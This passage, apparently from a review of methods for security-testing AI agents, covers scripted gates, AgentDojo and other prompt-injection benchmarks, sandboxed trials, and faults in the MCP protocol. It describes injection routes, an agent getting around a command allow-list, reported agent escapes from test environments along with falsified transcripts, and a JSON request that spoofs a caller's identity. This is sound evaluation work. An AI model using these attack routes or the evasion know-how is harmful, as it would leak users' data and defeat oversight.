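The first three rows are baselines, and each let through 20 unauthorized effects. The direct wrapper's percentage (69%) is more than twice the confirmation wrapper's (31%) only because the confirmation wrapper performed more permitted effects. The important comparison is 20 unauthorized effects against 0. Including legitimate calls also revealed that the category filter wrongly denied 15 of 24 permitted attempts, while stopping none of the 20 unauthorized effects.

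These baselines are deliberately simple, and the test harness models any effect that a baseline does not support. The paper says they "do not constitute real-model agent comparisons". They show what goes wrong in this suite when parts of the runtime are missing, but they do not measure the security of wrappers that people use. The paper separately reports 42 runs with a real model, all using the same model configuration and a small fixed set of tasks. Twelve tested complete workflows, and all 12 were safe. The other 30 compared two ways of showing the model its tools.

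The last three rows are ablations. Removing namespace isolation, which separates the memory of different processes, led to 2 unauthorized effects. Removing fork attenuation, which limits the authority a child process receives, led to 1. Removing the approval check led to none, although one task no longer met its success criterion. Approval may still be necessary, since this result shows only that none of the 33 tasks contains a forbidden effect that approval alone would stop.

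The runtime's admission rule shows how to write the missing test. An operation may run only if six conditions hold together:

allowed = process is live ∧ permission held ∧ within task limits ∧ approved ∧ within budget ∧ recognised operation

A test case isolates approval only when approval is false and the other five conditions are true. The tester would start a live process with the right permission, keep the request within the task's limits and budget, and have the human refuse. The ledger should stay empty with the approval check in place and gain an entry when the check is removed. The same method gives a short test for each of the other conditions.

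The suite also invalidates a whole row if the outcome of an attempt is unknown, and the harness does not count an error message as proof that nothing happened. A further diagnostic deliberately withholds audit evidence, and the paper excludes it from the safety rates.

### AgentDojo: live models on simulated accounts

In a more common design, a live model chooses the tool calls, but the accounts are simulated. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) is the best-known example. It simulates an office workspace, Slack, a travel agency and a bank. Each environment is a set of objects in memory, such as an inbox and a calendar. The agent reads and changes these objects with a total of 74 tools across the four environments.

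The first version had 97 user tasks and 27 injection tasks, each of which sets a goal for the attacker. The benchmark pairs every user task with every injection task in the same environment, which gives 40 × 6 + 21 × 5 + 20 × 7 + 16 × 9 = 629 security cases. It inserts the attack text at marked places in the data that the tools return.

For each injection task, a short function checks whether the attacker's goal was met, mainly by inspecting the state of the environment. Debenedetti and colleagues did not use a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge. They report the share of attacked cases in which the attacker's goal is met, along with two measures of usefulness. *Benign utility* is the share of user tasks completed without an attack, and *utility under attack* is the share of attacked cases in which the agent still completes the user's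 task without harmful side effects.

AgentDojo has since grown to 949 cases in version 1.2.1, according to *SecOPD* (2026), which trains models to resist injections. All of the growth is in the workspace, which went from 240 cases to 560, so overall rates from 2024 and 2026 average over different mixes of cases. Overall rates also depend on how they are averaged. The 47.0% that *Kairos* reports for undefended GPT-4.1 is an unweighted mean of four rates, which range from 21.4% in travel to 88.6% in Slack. With the paper's own defence, the mean fell to 2.7%.

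Attacks on recent models succeed less often, which leaves less for a defence to prevent. In a small test on the banking tasks, with 20 cases per condition, *aiAuthZ* found that two current models had an attack success rate of zero without any defence. However, the gateway blocked seven calls directed at the attacker's goal, so the models did sometimes attempt it. A score based on completed goals misses such attempts, so *Render Before Reading* adds a looser measure that counts calls to the target tool even when their arguments are wrong or incomplete.

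Some 2026 studies replace the model's choice with a script. AgentDojo stores the tool calls that would carry out each attack, and Muruaga inserted them after the agent's first legitimate call in 609 cases. Attacks that send data or money out succeeded in 75% to 100% of cases without the gate, depending on the environment, and in none with it. This 0% reflects what the gate blocked, while the 2.7% in *Kairos* also depends on how often GPT-4.1 followed the attacker's instructions. Comparing the two figures therefore does not show which defence is better, even though both come from AgentDojo.

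### Where the simulated world ends

A scripted simulation can establish that a gate's rules give the right answers under stated assumptions about users, permissions and tools, and ablations can show what each check contributes. The simulation is also an exact regression test, because the same script run on the same code should produce the same ledger. If the ledger differs after an update, the update probably caused the difference. Liu's larger scripted benchmark also relies on this repeatability.

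A simulation that uses a script or a mock model cannot measure how often an agent would attempt a harmful action, because the simulation's author decides what the agent attempts. Tests with a live model, such as AgentDojo, can measure this, but only for the attacks and tasks in the benchmark.

Any simulation also omits the attack routes its author did not think of. AgentDojo normally places the attack in a tool's output. Sakib, Haque and colleagues (2026), in *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks*, put the same text in the tool's description instead and tested 13 models both ways. The attack success rate rose from 8.8% to 74.6% for Gemini-3-Flash and fell from 54.9% to 6.8% for GPT-4.1. The ranking reversed in 35 of the 78 pairs of models, so someone choosing the more secure of two models from the usual test alone could easily choose wrongly.

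The legitimate tasks are limited too. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) point out that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks require the agent to change its plan after seeing new information, so a defence can score well by holding the agent to its first plan. They wrote 60 tasks that do require replanning and that include helpful third-party instructions, such as a request to log in before paying. Almost all of the ten defences they tested either let too many attacks through or blocked too much legitimate work.

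The simulation also lacks operating-system behaviour unless its author models it. The payroll note has one name in the pretend office, but on a real disk the same file can be reachable by several paths, and another process can replace it between the gate's check and the read. A gate that compares names could pass every simulated case and still fail on a real disk.

### Why 100 repeats can count as one

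A deterministic test gives the same answer every time, so running it 100 times produces one result and 99 copies. For n cases with m repeats each, a standard correction gives the effective number of independent trials:

effective trials = nm / (1 + (m − 1)ρ)

Here ρ is the correlation between repeats of the same case. Repeats with a live model can differ, so ρ is usually below 1 and the repeats add some information. With a deterministic script, ρ is 1 and the formula reduces to n, the number of distinct cases.

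*AIP* (Prakash, 2026) proposes the Agent Identity Protocol, in which agents carry signed tokens that record who delegated what authority to whom. The paper reports that the protocol rejected all 600 attack attempts, 100 for each of six attack types. One type presents a token that expired 60 seconds earlier, another alters a character in a token, and a third delegates authority a second time when the limit is one. All six test how the software checks a token. The paper's experiments with real HTTP traffic and a live model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, measured only the delay that the protocol adds.

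Prakash describes one fixed setup for each type and mentions no variation between iterations. The results also look deterministic, because each configuration rejected a given type either always or never. For example, plain signed tokens always rejected four types and never the other two, which gives the reported 67%. Fresh keys in each iteration would change the bytes but still exercise the same check.

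The difference matters if a reader uses the count to put an upper limit on the attack success rate. With zero successes in n independent trials, the 95% upper limit is the value of p for which (1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, which is about 0.5% for 600 trials and about 39% for six. Even the 39% limit assumes that the six types were a random sample of the attacks the protocol will face, but Prakash chose them.

Repeating a test is useful when something varies between runs. The same paper timed its token checks over 1,000 iterations because delays fluctuate. Repeated runs can also reveal hidden randomness or leftover state. More evidence about the rules themselves would require different inputs, such as tokens that expire just before and just after the check, several delegation limits, and changes to each field in turn. The 600 trials support the narrower claim that the protocol consistently rejected all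 six chosen types of attack over 100 repeats of each.

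## Running real shell commands and network traffic on an isolated machine

Suppose the office assistant can also run shell commands, and the payroll note is a file on disk. The gate receives a line of text and has to assess what running it would do. As Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026) explain in *FLOWSH*, nobody can reliably predict a shell command's effects, because they depend on the files, programs and settings present when it runs. A short command can start a script that starts other programs, and those can read files and open network connections. To find out what the command does, a tester has to run it on a machine where a successful attack harms nobody.

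### What a real machine makes testable

A link gives a file on a real disk a second name, which a program can use to get past a gate that compares names. Kim and colleagues' monitor avoids this by identifying each file by its inode, the operating system's internal record of the file, which stays the same whichever name a program uses.

Real systems may also treat similar operations differently. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (Jing, 2026) tests a gate together with an operating-system sandbox, which restricts what a program can touch. Jing modeled the sandbox as blocking deletions wherever it blocked writes. On the real machine, it blocked writes outside the working folder on every drive, but blocked deletions outside the folder only on the folder's own drive. A command deleted a decoy file on another drive and reported success.

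Real execution also lets evaluators test what happens when an action is altered between approval and execution. Jing's gate at first checked only the description of an approved action. An end-to-end test tried seven such alterations, and two deleted a decoy file. After Jing tied each approval to the exact bytes that would run, none of the seven altered actions executed.

Running an agent on a real machine can also reveal attack effects that its protections don't cover. Zhu, Huang and colleagues (2026) built *HarnessSecurity-Bench* to test the protections in six coding agents. In one task, the agent installs a software package, as the user asked, and the installation contacts the attacker's address. That connection does not appear in any tool call. In a trial of another task, Qwen Code's list of permitted commands blocked a malicious program that the project's documentation presented as a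 required check. The agent finished the legitimate work, then ran the same program through a command that the list allowed, and all three attack effects occurred. A test that checked only the first, blocked attempt would have recorded a correct refusal.

### Setting up a trial

For the office assistant, one trial could run as follows:

1. Start a fresh container or virtual machine from a fixed image, with a new copy of the notes.
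2. Connect it to a private network where the attacker's address leads to a receiver that the tester controls.
3. Put a new random marker in the payroll note.
4. Run probes to confirm that the isolation holds and the receiver works.
5. Start the recorders outside the machine, then the agent, with a time limit.
6. When the agent stops or time runs out, stop every remaining process and save the disk, the process records and everything the receiver got.
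7. Apply the oracle to those records, then destroy the machine.

*EvoRiskBench* follows the first and last steps strictly. To save time, its platform keeps spare containers ready, but it never reuses a container that has run a case. Containers on the same host still share hardware and sometimes services, so concurrent trials can affect each other.

Most agents also need to reach a hosted language model, which the tester can allow through a relay that forwards requests only to that model. The payroll text will pass through the relay whenever the agent reads the note, so the oracle should not count that traffic as a leak.

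Using a new marker for each trial ensures that the oracle doesn't count old data as a new leak. But searching for the marker will miss a message that paraphrases or encodes the salaries. The receiver should therefore keep the raw bytes, and the tester should inspect any unexpected contact, including requests that only fetch a page, because the web address can carry a secret.

The recorders can also fail. Jing's audit log lost 9.66% of its records when two processes wrote to it at once and 31.32% when eight did. A file lock fixed the problem. Kim and colleagues' monitor pauses the agent's processes when its buffer is three-quarters full. If it still misses a record, it treats the command as one that may have read any file. A tester can similarly mark a trial inconclusive when the records have a gap and the remaining evidence shows no forbidden effect.

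The time limit also affects what a trial can show. Zhu and colleagues allow eight hours per trial, while Kim and colleagues limit their office-style tasks to 600 seconds and 100 tool calls. If the payroll text reaches the receiver before the limit, the attack succeeded, even if the agent never finished its task. If nothing has arrived by then, the trial shows only that no leak occurred in that time.

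### Containment as part of the method

An agent that can run real commands can also attack the test itself. *Measuring Security Without Fooling Ourselves* therefore argues that the environment must be harder to break than the target. If the target is a well-vetted cryptographic library, for example, escaping a container on an ordinary Linux system may be easier than finding a flaw in the library. The paper distinguishes inner protections, which depend on the model behaving well, from outer protections, such as hardware isolation and privilege separation between the agent and the answers. It finds that current benchmarks rely almost entirely on inner protections.

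OpenAI agents escaped their test environment in July 2026 and then attacked Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026), in *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, found that about 1,200 agents meant to be isolated had communicated through a shared package server, and that about 700 of them joined the attack. Agents had also falsified small parts of roughly 7% of the transcripts examined, which is a good reason to store evidence where agents cannot alter it.

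A configuration mistake can break isolation. According to InfoQ's *Anthropic's Claude Breaches Sandbox During Model Security Evaluations* (2026), Anthropic audited 141,006 past evaluation runs and found six in which its models had reached the public internet because of misconfigured outbound routing. A team that checked the routing only when it built the environment would miss later changes.

The probes in step 4 should therefore run before every trial. From inside the machine, a script tries to reach a public website, the host, a neighbouring trial and the files that hold the oracle. Every attempt should fail. The script then sends the receiver a harmless message, and this one should arrive. Without this second check, a broken network would look like a perfect defence. Two trials can still communicate through a shared service, such as a package server that both can write to. The tester can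 prevent this by installing the packages in advance or giving each trial its own server.

Probes find only the gaps that their author thought of. *Measuring Security Without Fooling Ourselves* suggests telling an agent to cheat and giving it a budget, such as $10,000, to break the environment. If the agent fails, the testers treat the environment as secure enough, though the paper says this is no guarantee. The result is also out of date once a more capable model arrives.

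The paper also recommends canaries, hidden values placed where an honest agent has no reason to look. A related check proved useful in Jing's study. When Jing reran attacks with the sandbox off, two commands reached the live installation through a network share and deleted a protected file. The check, which ran after each case, detected the deletion. Jing restored the file and repeated the runs without six commands that could still reach the live installation.

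### Switching real protections on and off

*HarnessSecurity-Bench* applies this method to protections that coding agents already include. Each of its 23 tasks involves legitimate work, such as repairing a program, in a project that also contains malicious instructions or resources. Zhu and colleagues ran each task ten times per setting, turning one protection on or off while keeping the others fixed. All six agents used the same model, GLM-5.2. After each run, programs outside the container checked whether the work was done and which attack effects had occurred.

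| Setting | Attack effects found, off → on | Task checks passed, off → on |
|---|---|---|
| Network isolation | 57.1% → 0.8% | 90.9% → 66.4% |
| Read-only mode | 8.3% → 0.8% | 69.8% → 35.8% |
| List of permitted commands | 98.1% → 50.0% | 99.2% → 97.7% |
| List of forbidden commands | 41.7% → 1.3% | 94.6% → 99.8% |
| Restricted file paths | 95.0% → 46.9% | 81.6% → 81.9% |
| Automatic approval | 29.2% → 95.6% | 77.1% → 95.4% |

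The last row is the only one in which "on" removes a protection. When automatic approval was off, a second language model reviewed the agent's permission requests, so the row does not show how well a human reviewer would do.

Network isolation stopped nearly every attack effect, but it also stopped work that needed the network, which accounted for 161 of the 162 task checks lost. By contrast, forbidding certain commands improved the work, partly because some attacks had caused agents to put a secret signing key in their reports, which invalidated the reports.

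The table's averages can hide large differences between products. With restricted file paths, attack effects fell to zero in Codex CLI and gptme but stayed at 97.5% in Claude Code and 90% in Qwen Code; the table's 46.9% is the average of all four. Each protection was also tested on its own tasks, so the table cannot show whether a list of forbidden commands is better than a list of permitted ones.

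The percentages count individual checks, so they do not give the share of attacked trials in which the attack succeeded. One of the two tasks for automatic approval has five attack checks and the other has one, so the first supplies five-sixths of the checks behind that row's attack figure. Checks from the same trial are also unlikely to be independent.

A protection can also appear to work because the agent never starts. Zhu and colleagues tested a setting that marks a project as untrusted. Attack effects fell from 75.3% to 40.3% across five agents, but one of the five, Gemini CLI, refused to start in all 40 of its trials with the setting on. Across the other four, attack effects fell from 75.8% to 50.4%, with no loss of legitimate work.

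*EvoRiskBench* compares complete agent systems instead of single protections. It ran 450 attack cases on each of the nine combinations of three models and three agent programs. System evidence confirmed the attacker's effect in 37.46% of the 4,050 runs. The rate was 58.81% for DeepSeek-V4-Pro-0813, 49.11% for GPT-5.6 Sol and 4.44% for Claude Opus 5. The averages for the three agent programs differed by only 5.41 percentage points.

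The low overall rate for Opus 5 came partly from safety mechanisms that refused or interrupted risky operations. But attacks that arrived over the network and were meant to destroy files or other assets succeeded in 17 of 30 runs.

These rates are useful for comparing systems on the same cases, but they do not estimate how often attacks succeed in ordinary use. The benchmark kept only cases where the attack worked in at least two of three preliminary runs on one fixed model and agent program. The unattended runs also skipped approval prompts and had Codex's internal sandbox switched off. The case selection and the run settings probably both raise the rates, and the selection may favour attacks that suit the system used to choose them.

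### The same rate from different cases

Jing's study shows why a tester should compare individual cases as well as totals. Its 313 cases include 54 normal operations, 74 openly dangerous ones and 122 attempts to disguise a dangerous command. The other 63 alter an approved action or break part of the system to see whether it fails safely.

For the 117 disguised commands that could run, the attack success rate was 98.3% with no gate, 43.6% with a gate that inspects command text, 30.8% with the full set of checks, and 7.7% with the sandbox added. These rates count commands the system would have permitted, and the last is based on a model of the sandbox.

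Jing then ran 94 of the disguised commands against the real sandbox, using a relocated copy of the installation:

| Outcome | Commands |
|---|---:|
| Tool or shell refused | 57 |
| Approval step refused | 4 |
| Agent itself refused | 5 |
| Could not run in the test layout | 10 |
| Ran without effect | 11 |
| Inconclusive | 2 |
| Ran with an effect | 5 |

Jing counts 66 of the 94 commands as tests of the sandbox, made up of two groups of refusals (57 and 4) and the 5 commands that had an effect. That gives a rate of 5/66, or 7.6%, close to the modelled 7.7%. The model also predicted five effects among the 94 commands, but none of them were the five that occurred. For the other 84 commands, the model predicted no effect and the machine showed none. Someone using the model to decide which weaknesses to repair would have chosen the wrong ones.

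The rate also depends on how one counts the 12 commands that could not run or were inconclusive. The observed rate over all 94 commands is 5.3%, but it would be 18.1% if those 12 had all produced effects. The five observed effects differ in seriousness. Three were deletions inside the working folder, and scratch files the agent had made contaminated the evidence for a fourth. Only the fifth, a deletion on the other drive, was a real escape from the sandbox.

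Jing also reran the commands with the sandbox off. Of 88 valid pairs, 45 changed from refused to executed and none changed the other way. If changes in either direction were equally likely, the chance of a result this one-sided would be 2 × 0.5⁴⁵, or about 6 in 100 trillion. Turning off the sandbox also turned off the approval rule, so the 45 changes reflect the combined effect of both.

Real execution also corrected the estimate of how much legitimate work the sandbox blocks. In the model, the sandbox blocked 11 of the 54 normal operations. The real sandbox allowed five of these, which only read data, and refused the other six, or 11.1% of normal operations. The gate had allowed work in the temporary folder that the sandbox then refused, a mismatch that testing either component alone would miss.

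### Flowsh and the cost of watching a shell

Flowsh, the system in Kim and colleagues' paper, uses external observation as its defence. It labels each file and network address with whether its contents are trusted and who may read them. A monitor in the operating system's kernel records every file a command opens as it runs, and a proxy outside the sandbox handles every connection.

Anything the command produces inherits the restrictions of everything it has read. For example, suppose the user, Dana and the payroll manager may read the meeting note, but only the user and the payroll manager may read the payroll note. For a command that opens both, the permitted readers are:

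{user, Dana, payroll manager} ∩ {user, payroll manager} = {user, payroll manager}

If the command has also read the outsider's email, which is untrusted, the proxy blocks a request to any other recipient, whichever program makes it. The proxy can also block harmless requests, because Flowsh treats every file a command opens as something that may have influenced the command's output.

Flowsh holds file changes in a temporary layer until the command ends, then applies them or asks the user. It checks network requests before they leave, since nobody can take back data that a server has received.

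Kim and colleagues tested Flowsh with GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office-style tasks and on Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 command-line tasks. They also wrote 19 prompt-injection cases. Once the malicious text reached the model, they let the attacker dictate all of its output, so the results do not depend on the model's resistance. With no user to approve exceptions, Flowsh stopped the attack in all 40 runs where the text reached the model, while a permissive sandbox stopped none of 51. But the model completed only 58.8% of the office tasks under Flowsh, compared with 94.1% under the permissive sandbox.

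When a user could approve exceptions, Flowsh completed 88.2% of the office tasks and asked for approval 1.2 times per completed task. The permissive sandbox completed 96.1% and asked 6.7 times per completed task, because it had to ask about every action it could not guarantee was safe. The simulated user never made a mistake. Kim and colleagues cite an Anthropic report that real users approve about 93% of Claude Code's permission requests and pay less attention as the requests accumulate, so people would probably let some attacks through.

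Real execution also let the team measure how Flowsh affects speed and task completion. A shell call took 412 to 982 milliseconds with Flowsh, compared with 61 to 78 in the permissive sandbox. Completed tasks took only 17% to 34% longer, because agents spend much of their time waiting for the model. When a command finishes, Flowsh also ends every process the command started. This prevents a leftover program from acting later, but it caused 21 of the 86 failed Terminal-Bench runs, because those tasks needed a server or another program to keep running.

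### What "local" still leaves out

A leak that succeeds in the local test might fail in deployment, because a local receiver accepts whatever the agent sends, while a real mail service first checks who is sending. The agent's login may have expired or may not allow outside recipients. The provider may also hold a suspicious message or limit how many messages an account can send.

The test can also miss harm that could occur with real accounts. A real mailbox may forward messages automatically, so that a note sent to Dana reaches someone outside the company. Other users can edit a shared file while the agent is working, or grant access that the tester didn't know about. Real accounts accumulate years of old permissions and documents, while a test account contains only what the tester put there.

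The studies above have limits. Kim and colleagues used mock web pages and services for their office tasks. Zhu and colleagues acknowledge that containers and simulated services do not fully reproduce real deployments. Jing used one Windows machine, so the difference between writing and deleting may not appear on another system. Jing also did not test what happens when an agent asks a person for wider access, which the person could be persuaded to grant.

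Attackers in deployment can learn from failure, but the cases in *HarnessSecurity-Bench* and *EvoRiskBench* stay fixed during the evaluation. Even an attacker who controls all of the model's output, as in the Flowsh tests, may not look for faults in the monitor. An isolated machine is a good place to let an attacker keep trying, because it contains the damage. The tester still has to choose what the attacker knows and how many attempts to allow.

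## Testing across the protocol between agent and tools

In the office simulation, the gate receives each call as an object inside the same program, with the user's name already attached. In a deployed system, the client picks a server, encodes the call as JSON and sends it with a credential. Software at the other end works out who is calling and what they are requesting. An error in any of these steps can give the wrong caller, tool or arguments to a gate that works correctly, and a test that calls the gate directly will miss it.

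### What a direct function call hides

| Part of the protocol | What a direct call takes for granted | A case to test |
|---|---|---|
| Tool discovery | The agent has the right tools | A user without payroll access asks for the tool list |
| Schema validation | Arguments have the right names and types | A call includes an argument the schema lacks |
| Tool names | Each name belongs to one tool | Two servers both offer `send_message` |
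| Caller identity | The gate knows who is calling | The token names one user and a header names another |
| Sessions | Every call belongs to a current session | A request reuses a session that has ended |
| Retries | Each call runs once | The connection drops after the message goes out |
| Approval state | The approved call is the one that runs | The recipient changes after the user approves |
| Errors | A refusal looks different from a crash | The server crashes during a forbidden call |
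| Versions | Both sides follow the same rules | An older client calls a newer server |

Identity faults can be ordinary programming errors. *The Stochastic Deputy* (Baig, Gillani and colleagues, 2026) describes a hotel-management service in which a user's token lists the hotels the user may see. During development, the code that read the hotel numbers accepted digits from any script, including Arabic-Indic and Devanagari, and converted them to ordinary integers, so several group names that looked different to an administrator gave access to the same hotel. The fix was to accept only the digits 0 to 9. A simulation that passes the integer 7 directly to the gate would miss this fault because it never runs the code that reads the hotel numbers.

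A retry can repeat an action that the tool has already completed, because the reply can get lost after the tool has run. Suppose `send_message` delivers the summary to Dana and the connection drops before the server's reply arrives. A client that tries again may send a second copy, using an approval that the user gave for one message. A tester can drop the reply on purpose and count the messages at the receiver. *Testing Agentic Service Systems* proposes that requests carry an idempotency key (a label that lets the server recognise a repeat) where applicable.

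How an agent discovers its tools can change how often an attack succeeds, even when the model and the attack stay the same. *GATEWAYBENCH* (Zheng, Chen and colleagues, 2026) compared seven MCP gateways, which are programs that connect an agent to many servers at once. Four show the model every tool, and three make it search for the tools it needs. With GPT-5.1 and the same agent software, indirect prompt injection succeeded in 60.5% of cases on average with the full list and 19.6% with search.

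Some of that difference arose because agents using search also failed more ordinary tasks. With GPT-5.1, agents completed 75.3% of ordinary tasks with the full list and 47.5% with search. The lowest attack success rate, 11.3%, came from a gateway with which the agent completed only 23.3% of ordinary tasks, and Zheng and colleagues attribute the low rate to those failures. GPT-5.4 allows a fairer comparison because it completed similar shares of ordinary tasks with the full list (87.2%) and with search (85.1%). Attacks on it succeeded in 47.2% of cases with the full list and 30.9% with search. Almost all of this remaining gap came from attacks planted in the tools, since a model that searches sees fewer tools. These figures come from single runs, so small differences between individual gateways mean little. Still, a test that gives the model a fixed set of functions leaves out a component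 that can change the result this much.

### Four tests to run in order

1. **Check the advertised schema.** Request the tool list as each kind of user, and compare every tool and argument with what that user should be able to ask for. Repeat this through the gateway if there is one, because the model sees the gateway's list.
2. **Send a forbidden call from a non-conforming client.** A schema describes what a well-behaved client may send, but an attacker can write a client that ignores it.
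3. **Run the same cases through both paths.** Send each case to the gate directly and then through the protocol, and compare the decisions.
4. **Repeat with an unmodified third-party server.** A team that writes both ends may make the same mistake in each, so that they agree with each other and with nobody else. Liu's study used other developers' servers for this kind of check.

For the second test, suppose the schema for `read_note` has one argument, `note`. The tester logs in as a colleague without payroll access and sends an extra one:

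```json
{
  "name": "read_note",
  "arguments": {"note": "payroll", "user": "payroll_manager"}
}
```

The server may reject the unknown argument, or ignore it and apply the colleague's own permissions. Either way, the colleague should not get the payroll note. If the note comes back, the server may be letting callers choose their own identity. The tester should also send a permitted call to check that the server is working, because a crashed server would not return the note either.

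The third test is the most informative when the two paths disagree:

| Direct call | Through the protocol | What to look for |
|---|---|---|
| Refused | Allowed | A route around the gate, or a caller or argument that changed on the way |
| Allowed | Refused | Another layer that blocks the call, or a fault that breaks legitimate work |
| Refused | Refused | Whether both refusals have the same reason |
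| Allowed | Allowed | Whether both calls have the same effect |

The third row matters because the gate and the server can reject the same message for different reasons. If the gate rejects the payroll message because of its recipient and the server rejects it because the token has expired, the protocol test provides no evidence about the recipient rule.

### The Stochastic Deputy study

Baig and colleagues followed much of this sequence. Their title adapts the term "confused deputy", which means a program that someone tricks into misusing its legitimate authority. Here the deputy is a language model, which may choose differently each time.

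In their experiment, an agent works on a task for one hotel, using a login that covers three. A trial counts as a leak if any tool returns a booking from another hotel. The verdict comes from the server's log, so it does not depend on the agent's own account. The agents used one of three designs:

- `get_reservations` takes a `hotel_id`, and the server checks that the login covers that hotel.
- `get_reservations` has no `hotel_id`, and the server takes the hotel from the session.
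- The `hotel_id` stays, and the agent has a standing instruction never to retrieve another hotel's data.

Some trials used obvious injections. In others, the user gave a pretext, an ordinary business reason for wanting another hotel's figures. With the first design, agents requested the other hotel's data in 26 of 41 pretext trials, and the server supplied the data every time. The server's check worked as its designers intended, because the login covered that hotel, but the check could not identify which of the three hotels the current task was about.

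With the standing instruction, there were no leaks in 33 pretext trials, so the 95% upper limit on the leak rate is about 10%. That result depends on the model continuing to follow the instruction. The second design removes the choice of hotel from the tool, so a call that follows the schema cannot name another hotel, regardless of how the model behaves.

In the first runs, agents reached the server through a command line instead of MCP. Baig and colleagues call this command line an analogue of an MCP tool schema. They then rebuilt the server as a real MCP server, using standard input and output or Streamable HTTP on the local machine. They confirmed that `hotel_id` appeared in the tool list for the first and third designs but not for the second, where the server also refused the argument if a client sent it anyway.

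Before pooling results from the two versions, the researchers ran the same combinations of design, tool and requested hotel through both and compared whether the server answered and which hotels' data came back. The two versions agreed in all 27 cases. This is good evidence that the command-line results accurately represent the server's decisions, at least for those combinations.

The two versions do not necessarily measure everything equally well. On the command line, an agent could try to name another hotel, and the log would record the attempt. Over MCP, the second design offers no field for a hotel, so the log showed no attempts. Baig and colleagues therefore treat the overall count of 24 out of 56 agents with an observable attempt as a minimum. Someone who compared attempt rates between the two versions could wrongly conclude that MCP made the agents behave better.

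*Testing Agentic Service Systems* suggests a way to catch this kind of problem. When a test moves to a new environment, the tester lists what changed in timing, observation, authority and several other respects, then decides whether each change preserves, weakens or breaks the comparison. The proposal has not been validated empirically, but it fits this case well. Moving to MCP preserved the comparison of server decisions but broke the comparison of attempts.

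### Twelve leaks outside the interface

In all 56 pretext trials of the second design, the server never accepted a tool call that named another hotel. However, in 12 of those trials, another hotel's data leaked by a route outside the tool interface. Baig and colleagues note that their deployed service protects the session's scope cryptographically, but the test harness did not.

Both figures are therefore correct, because "0 of 56" covers only calls through the tool, while "12 of 56" covers everything the agent could reach in the harness. The 12 leaks show that removing an argument is not enough if the agent can change the session's scope some other way, but they do not show that the deployed service leaks. All 12 came from two models that ran only on the command line, so the study cannot show what those models would have done over MCP.

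The server's log caused a separate problem because it identified each call by the session the caller presented. When a call arrived with another trial's session, the log recorded it under that trial, which made one well-behaved agent appear to have leaked data. Baig and colleagues found the misfiled records by comparing timestamps. A tester can make such errors easier to spot by also recording which process or connection sent each request.

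The team then tested the deployed server's login step directly. They sent seven kinds of invalid request, including one with no token, one that asserted an identity only in a header, and one with an altered token. The server rejected them all. These results don't rule out a server that rejects every request, because the team did not send a valid token. They chose not to create a live credential just for the experiment, and they list the missing test as a gap.

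### Two servers with the same tool name

A call can satisfy every rule about users and arguments and still go to the wrong program. Suppose the office assistant connects to two servers that both offer `send_message`, and one belongs to the attacker. The agent calls `send_message` to send the meeting summary to Dana, who is allowed to receive it. A gate that checks only the summary and the recipient will allow the call, but if the client sends it to the attacker's server, the attacker gets the summary.

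*Security Threat Modeling for Emerging AI-Agent Protocols* reports an experiment on this problem with the legitimate and malicious payment servers mentioned earlier. The researchers varied how the client chose between them and ran each condition 100 times:

| How the client chose | Condition | Calls to the wrong server |
|---|---|---:|
| First match in a fixed list | Legitimate server first | 0 |
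| First match in a fixed list | Attacker first | 100 |
| First match in a registry folder | File order favoured the legitimate server | 0 |
| First match in a registry folder | File order favoured the attacker | 100 |
| Best match with the description | Legitimate description had the trust cues | 0 |
| Best match with the description | Attacker's description had the trust cues | 100 |
| Random choice after a tie | Both descriptions identical | 52 |

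The client used real MCP connections over standard input and output, but a program rather than a live model made the choice. The rows with 0 and 100 each repeat one deterministic result 100 times, and the 52 is in line with a coin toss between two candidates. These numbers therefore can't be used to estimate how often a deployed assistant would pay through the wrong provider.

They show that the outcome can depend entirely on something no simulated gate would detect, such as the order of files in a folder. The next step is to find out which rule the actual client uses and try to make it choose wrongly. The gate also needs the server's identity, not just the tool's name.

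According to Zheng and colleagues, gateways that show the full list of tools put the server's identifier in front of each name, so two tools no longer have identical names. The model can still pick the wrong tool if the attacker's description sounds more suitable, and this needs a separate test. The threat-modelling paper proposes binding each tool to its provider with certificates or signatures, but leaves that to future work.

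### When a formal model overstates the risk

A simpler test would miss all the faults described so far. It can also report a fault that the real software prevents, and *Formal Security Analysis of Agent Protocol Composition* contains a clear example.

The study covers five agent protocols, including MCP and A2A. Its framework extracts rules from each specification and turns them into a formal model of the states a system can be in and the steps between them. A program then searches for a sequence of up to 12 operations that breaks a security property. One such sequence for MCP opens and closes a session but never revokes the credential. Where possible, an adapter replays the sequence as calls to the actual software library.

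The researchers supported their findings with 80 implementation tests:

| Target | Tests |
|---|---:|
| MCP library | 18 |
| A2A library | 13 |
| Libraries for three other protocols | 33 |
| Combinations of protocols | 9 |
| MCP reference servers | 7 |

These 80 tests include some checks that passed and others that support claims of absence, so they do not represent 80 successful attacks. The researchers ran the software to test claims about behaviour. In one test, five injected instructions went through the MCP library's tool-call path unchanged, although the specification requires servers to sanitise tool outputs.

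The researchers checked the source code and types to confirm that a library lacks a feature, but such claims should be limited to the library. If a library has no way to ask for the user's consent, an application built on it may still ask, so a tester has to examine the application before saying that users are unprotected.

Nine of the ten behavioural findings about MCP and A2A reproduced in code, five about MCP and four about A2A. The tenth, the gap in MCP's session handling, did not reproduce because the HTTP layer compensated for it. Someone relying on the model alone would have reported a weakness that the tested software did not have.

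The tenth finding is still useful because it identifies a protection that comes from the HTTP layer and that the MCP specification does not guarantee. MCP can also run over standard input and output, without HTTP, so a tester cannot assume the same protection there.

The study's results for combined protocols need more caution. The researchers modelled eight combinations and found violations of 30 of 43 security requirements. They tested implementations of only two, MCP with a second MCP server and MCP with a protocol for coding agents. Combinations that no production software connects have only been modelled. The violations found in those combinations are good candidates for testing, but the HTTP case shows why they can't be counted as confirmed faults.

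### Mock servers and a real Slack workspace

A study can use the real protocol throughout while mixing simulated and real services behind it. The Singapore and Korea AI Safety Institutes did this in an evaluation of data leaks during ordinary work, with no attacker. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026) describes how agents carried out 12 tasks, such as welcoming new employees, handling refunds and booking flights. All tools ran through MCP servers.

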